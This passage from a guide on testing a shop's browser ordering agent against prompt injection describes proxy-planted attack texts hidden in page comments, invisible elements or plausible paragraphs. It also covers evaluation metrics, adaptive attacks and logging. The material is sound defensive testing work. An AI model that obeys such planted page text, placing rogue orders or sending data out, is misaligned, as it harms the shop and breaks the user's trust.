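At the earlier estimate of 294,000 input tokens for a 12-step order, 360 runs would use about 106 million input tokens. With caching, these would cost the same as about 24 million at full price.

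### Real pages or a closed copy

The planted text has to be on a page that the assistant may visit. Chen, Toyoda and colleagues (2026), in *IPI-proxy*, describe an open-source proxy that inserts it into real pages in transit:

1. The agent requests a page from a permitted site, and the proxy forwards the request unchanged.
2. The site returns its real HTML. The proxy checks that the address matches the tester's pattern.
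3. The proxy picks one of 820 attack texts that Chen and colleagues collected from six published benchmarks.
4. It wraps the text in an HTML comment, an invisible element or a plausible paragraph, and inserts it at one of six places in the page.
5. The agent receives the altered page. If it obeys an instruction to send data to the tester's tracking server, that server logs the request.

The site itself doesn't change, so no other visitor receives the text. Chen and colleagues give no results from tests on agents, so it is unclear how many weaknesses the proxy would find.

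A tester could easily misuse the proxy on the shop's order agent. The proxy plants one attack in an HTML comment, one in an element hidden with `display:none`, and one in a plausible paragraph. The agent reads snapshots, which leave out comments and hidden elements, so only the paragraph would reach the model. The tester could record hundreds of failures for the other two attacks, which the model never read.

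*Silent Failures in Agentic Security Evaluation* (Shaw, 2026) reports the same kind of fault in an existing benchmark, where 39 of 43 attack texts never reached the agent. The benchmark still counted each of the 39 as an attack that the agent could have followed. The test software should therefore search the model's input for the planted text and exclude any run where that text is missing.

The tracking server also misses some failures. The shop's network rules would block requests to it, so its log would stay empty even if the model had followed the text's instructions. A blocked request in the egress proxy's log shows that the model followed them and the network rule prevented the harm, which is worth recording separately. An order for 40 pumps wouldn't appear in the tracking server's log either, because placing it sends no request to that server.

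A successful attack on a live site has real consequences, such as the supplier shipping the 40 pumps. A closed copy of the site is safer for testing any job that places orders, changes an account, publishes text or handles customer data. It also spares the supplier hundreds of automated visits and lets the tester reset everything between runs. And it stops the agent from looking up answers online, which CAISI, the U.S. government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation, saw GPT-5 do in a hacking test.

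Chen and colleagues object that an agent limited to approved sites can't reach imitation pages unless the tester relaxes the limit, which invalidates the test. The tester can avoid this by having the egress proxy send requests for `supplier3.example` to an imitation site that presents a certificate the test browser accepts. The list of approved sites can then stay the same as in production.

A copy of a website includes only the behavior its developer thought of, so it may lack the slow confirmation page that leads to a duplicate order. The shop could test its price comparison agent on live public pages through IPI-proxy and its order agent on a copy, then watch the first few real orders closely.

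### Three figures to report

*Kairos* (2026), which tests a security layer for agents, uses three measures that together describe a defense:

- Task success without attack is the share of ordinary runs in which the agent completes the user's job.
- Task success under attack is the share of attacked runs in which it still completes the user's job.
- Attack success rate is the share of attacked runs in which it completes the attacker's goal.

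The next table uses invented results for the repair shop.

| Setup | Task success without attack | Task success under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| No added defense | 57 of 60 (95%) | 261 of 300 (87%) | 18 of 300 (6%) |
| Block every tool call | 0 of 60 (0%) | 0 of 300 (0%) | 0 of 300 (0%) |
| The shop's limits | 54 of 60 (90%) | 264 of 300 (88%) | 0 of 300 (0%) |

On attack success rate alone, the setup that blocks everything ties for first place, although it can't order a single pump.

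A defense can stop most attacks and still keep the agent from completing many of its tasks. In *CT0* (2026), a filter with fixed text patterns stopped all 64 attacks, but the agent completed only 18 of the 64 attacked tasks, compared with 42 without the filter. A guard that used a language model let two attacks through, but with it the agent failed only one of the 23 ordinary tasks it had completed without a guard. Most deployers would prefer the language-model guard. *Kairos* reports a detector that kept the attack success rate low, but the agent completed only 0.6 percent of tasks under attack.

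A weak model can also look safe because it is incompetent. Shaw reported one model's security as unmeasurable because it failed all ten trivial tool tasks.

Some forbidden outcomes will occur without an injection. If the assistant accepts the supplier's offer of a fifth pump in two of the 60 ordinary runs, a few five-pump orders in the attacked runs may be the same mistake. *Confidently Wrong* (2026) runs the same documents without the injection and subtracts the rate of forbidden outcomes in those runs from the rate in the attacked runs. The shop should report the rates with and without the injection, because it pays for the fifth pump whether or not an injection caused the order.

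### How scoring rules change the result

Shaw rescored 258 recorded attack runs under two rules. The attack success rate was 21.7 percent when the agent only had to use the tool the attacker wanted, and 1.2 percent when the tool's arguments also had to match the attacker's goal. The first rule counted runs in which the agent used that tool for the user's task. It would be useless for the repair shop, because every legitimate order uses `browser_click`.

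In *Evaluating a Layered Prompt-Injection Defence for the Model Context Protocol*, Abasıkeleş-Turgut and Gümüş (2026) audited CASCADE, their own system for screening text before it reaches an MCP host. CASCADE can allow a text, block it or refer it to a person. They ran it on 5,000 texts, 1,521 of them harmless.

If a referral counts as an alarm, CASCADE without its optional review model caught 94.77 percent of the attacks and raised false alarms on 11.70 percent of the harmless texts. If only a block counts, the same run caught 0.80 percent of the attacks and raised false alarms on 1.51 percent of the harmless texts. Neither definition gives both the high detection rate and the low false alarm rate.

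Neither rule shows how much work is left for people. CASCADE referred 68.5 percent of all texts to a person. That would be too many for a shop, but the share was high partly because about 70 percent of the texts in the test set were attacks. It referred 155 of the harmless texts, or about 10 percent. If the shop screened one text at each of 12 steps and placed 240 orders a year, that rate would add about 290 needless prompts to the 240 approvals the owner already gives. A report should therefore list allowed, referred and blocked texts separately for ordinary traffic.

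The audit also found that two thirds of the texts had been made by putting another text inside one of five fixed wrappers, and that the wrapper revealed whether the text was an attack. A rule that checked only the wrapper caught 72.84 percent of the attacks with no false alarms, which beat CASCADE's standalone engine of 93 patterns. The shop's test could have the same flaw if every planted instruction began with "IMPORTANT" and no harmless review did, so some harmless reviews should use the same wording, such as "Important: this pump needs the newer gasket."

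CASCADE's decisions also depended on the order of the texts. Its blocking threshold stopped 24 attacks among the first 48 texts and none afterwards, because the software was still calibrating itself at the start. When twelve of those texts appeared again later, CASCADE only referred them. Shuffling the runs and repeating some of them late in the test can expose this kind of fault.

### What a clean result proves

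Suppose none of the 300 attacked runs ends in a forbidden outcome. If the runs are independent and the true rate is *p*, the chance of such a result is (1 − *p*)^300. The 95 percent upper bound is the rate at which that chance drops to 5 percent:

```
(1 − p)^300 = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 0.0099
```

If no attack succeeds in 300 test runs, the true success rate could still be about 1 percent. Dividing 3 by the number of clean runs gives this approximate upper bound, at 95 percent confidence. According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, attacks on Claude Opus 5 failed in all 129 browser scenarios that Anthropic tested. If each scenario counts as one independent trial, the upper bound is 2.3 percent, so this strong result doesn't establish that the problem is solved.

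A rate of 1 percent matters if an attacker can keep trying. Over 100 independent attempts, the chance of at least one success is:

```
1 − (1 − 0.01)^100 ≈ 0.63
```

Three hundred clean runs can't rule out a roughly 63 percent chance that an attacker succeeds at least once in 100 attempts. Ruling out a chance above 10 percent would take about 3,000 clean runs. For a small shop, a low credit limit is a cheaper way to reduce the risk.

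The shop's 300 runs aren't independent, because they consist of 100 attacked versions run three times each. If all three runs of a version always ended the same way, the 300 runs would count as only 100 trials, and the upper bound would be about 3 percent. With only ten texts run 30 times each, the bound could be as high as 26 percent. Writing more texts therefore usually improves the estimate more than adding repeats.

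An attacker's attempts aren't independent either. The table compares measured rates for four Claude models with the rates expected if attempts were independent. The figures come from CAISI's *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, VentureBeat, and the Opus 5 system card as quoted in Schneier's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026).

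| Model | One attempt | Repeated attempts, measured | If attempts were independent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 57% | 80% after 25 | Nearly 100% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 63% after 100 | 99% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, operating a graphical interface | 17.8% | 78.6% after 200 | Nearly 100% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% within 15 | 3.0% |

The measured rates are lower because targets differ in how often they fail, which an average does not show. An average of 1 percent could mean that every page fails in 1 percent of attempts, or that one page in 100 always fails and the rest never do. With 100 attempts on a randomly chosen page, the attacker would have a 63 percent chance of succeeding at least once in the first case and a 1 percent chance in the second.

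Testers need to measure the attack success rate separately for each forbidden outcome. CAISI's 57 percent success rate is an average over five attacker goals, ranging from sending a harmless email to stealing and deleting files. These goals differed widely in both success rate and damage.

### Attackers who adapt

The formula can also understate the danger because it doesn't account for attackers learning between attempts. CAISI and the UK's AI Security Institute used some of a benchmark's tasks to write new attacks specifically for Claude 3.5 Sonnet, then tried them on tasks they had set aside. The strongest new attack succeeded 81 percent of the time, compared with 11 percent for the strongest older one. That model dates from 2024, but the effect persists in newer ones. In *The Devil is in the Context* (2026), an undefended agent with a recent model resisted every attack in cases selected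 from an existing benchmark, but attacks succeeded in 17.5 percent of newly generated cases.

A fixed test set therefore makes a deployment look safer than it is, and more so each time a developer uses it to tune a defense. The tester should set aside some of the planted texts until the configuration is final, and write new ones after any failure. Public attack collections are less useful than their size suggests. Dziemian and colleagues published 95 attacks that had worked on an open model, Qwen, but they chose ones that hadn't transferred to any closed-source model, so resisting all 95 is little evidence that a closed-source model is secure.

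Adapting an attack to the defense may help less when the limits are outside the model. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) tested an attack adapted to Progent, a system that checks tool calls against a policy. The adapted attack succeeded 2.6 percent of the time, compared with 4.2 percent for the standard attack. But the test used a single handwritten attack on one weak model, so the low rate could be due to a poor attack rather than a good defense. The shop should still try to get around its own rules, using methods such as redirects, unusual address formats and misleading button names.

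### What to log, and when to stop

After release, somebody has to be able to reconstruct an order without asking the assistant what it did.

| What to log | Details | Stop the assistant if |
|---|---|---|
| Tool calls | Arguments, results and times | It tries to submit the same order twice |
| Origins contacted | Every host, taken from the proxy's log | Traffic reaches a host that isn't on the list |
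| Confirmations | The exact text shown, the answer and the resulting order | An order has no approval or differs from the approved one |
| Blocked requests | The rule that applied and the page read just before | Several occur in one job, or the same page precedes blocks in different jobs |

One blocked request is often harmless, because the supplier's site may have started loading a script from a new company, but three in one job suggest that the assistant is trying to get around a limit. Chrome for Developers notes that attacks often push an agent outside its normal behavior, and recommends combining live alerts with later analysis of the logs. For example, if an order normally uses 300,000 tokens, one that uses a million should trigger an alert.

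To stop the assistant, the host should end the session. The owner should cancel the saved login, in case someone has copied it, and check the supplier's order history. The host and the proxy should write their logs where the agent can't change them, and leave out passwords and cookies. The logs will still contain trade prices and addresses, so the shop should limit who can read them and should delete them after a fixed period.

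### Changes that require a new test

A test result applies only to the setup that produced it. The host can store the tested model version, the server version, a checksum of the tool definitions and the list of permitted sites, then refuse to start if any of them has changed. *Decision Hijacking* (2026) applies a similar rule in its experiments and treats a wrong model version as a failure.

Yang and colleagues ran the same scanner for malicious agent add-ons with nine models, changing nothing else. Its false alarm rate ranged from 1.2 to 18.7 percent. Providers sometimes update a model without changing its name, so the shop should request a dated version where one exists.

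A server update can rename a tool, add one or change what a snapshot contains. Changes to safeguards need the same care. In Anthropic's tests, the attack success rate for Claude Opus 4.5 in a browser fell from 7.6 to 1.4 percent when only the safeguards changed. Another update could raise the rate.

**Tool description.** Even an honest rewording can change which tool the model picks. The checksum also catches a "rug pull".

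A new supplier's site has new forms, new reviewers and possibly new advertisers. When the shop adds one to its permitted sites, it has to write new planted texts for that site, because the old ones test pages that the assistant can already handle.

The method of reading or operating pages also belongs on this list. VentureBeat reports that attacks on Claude Opus 4.6 failed in all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment, but succeeded in 17.8 percent of single attempts when the model operated a graphical interface. If the shop turns on screenshots and coordinate clicks to read a parts diagram, its earlier test results no longer apply.

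After a change, the tester should run the 60 ordinary jobs first, because 300 attacked runs aren't worth paying for if the assistant can no longer place a normal order.
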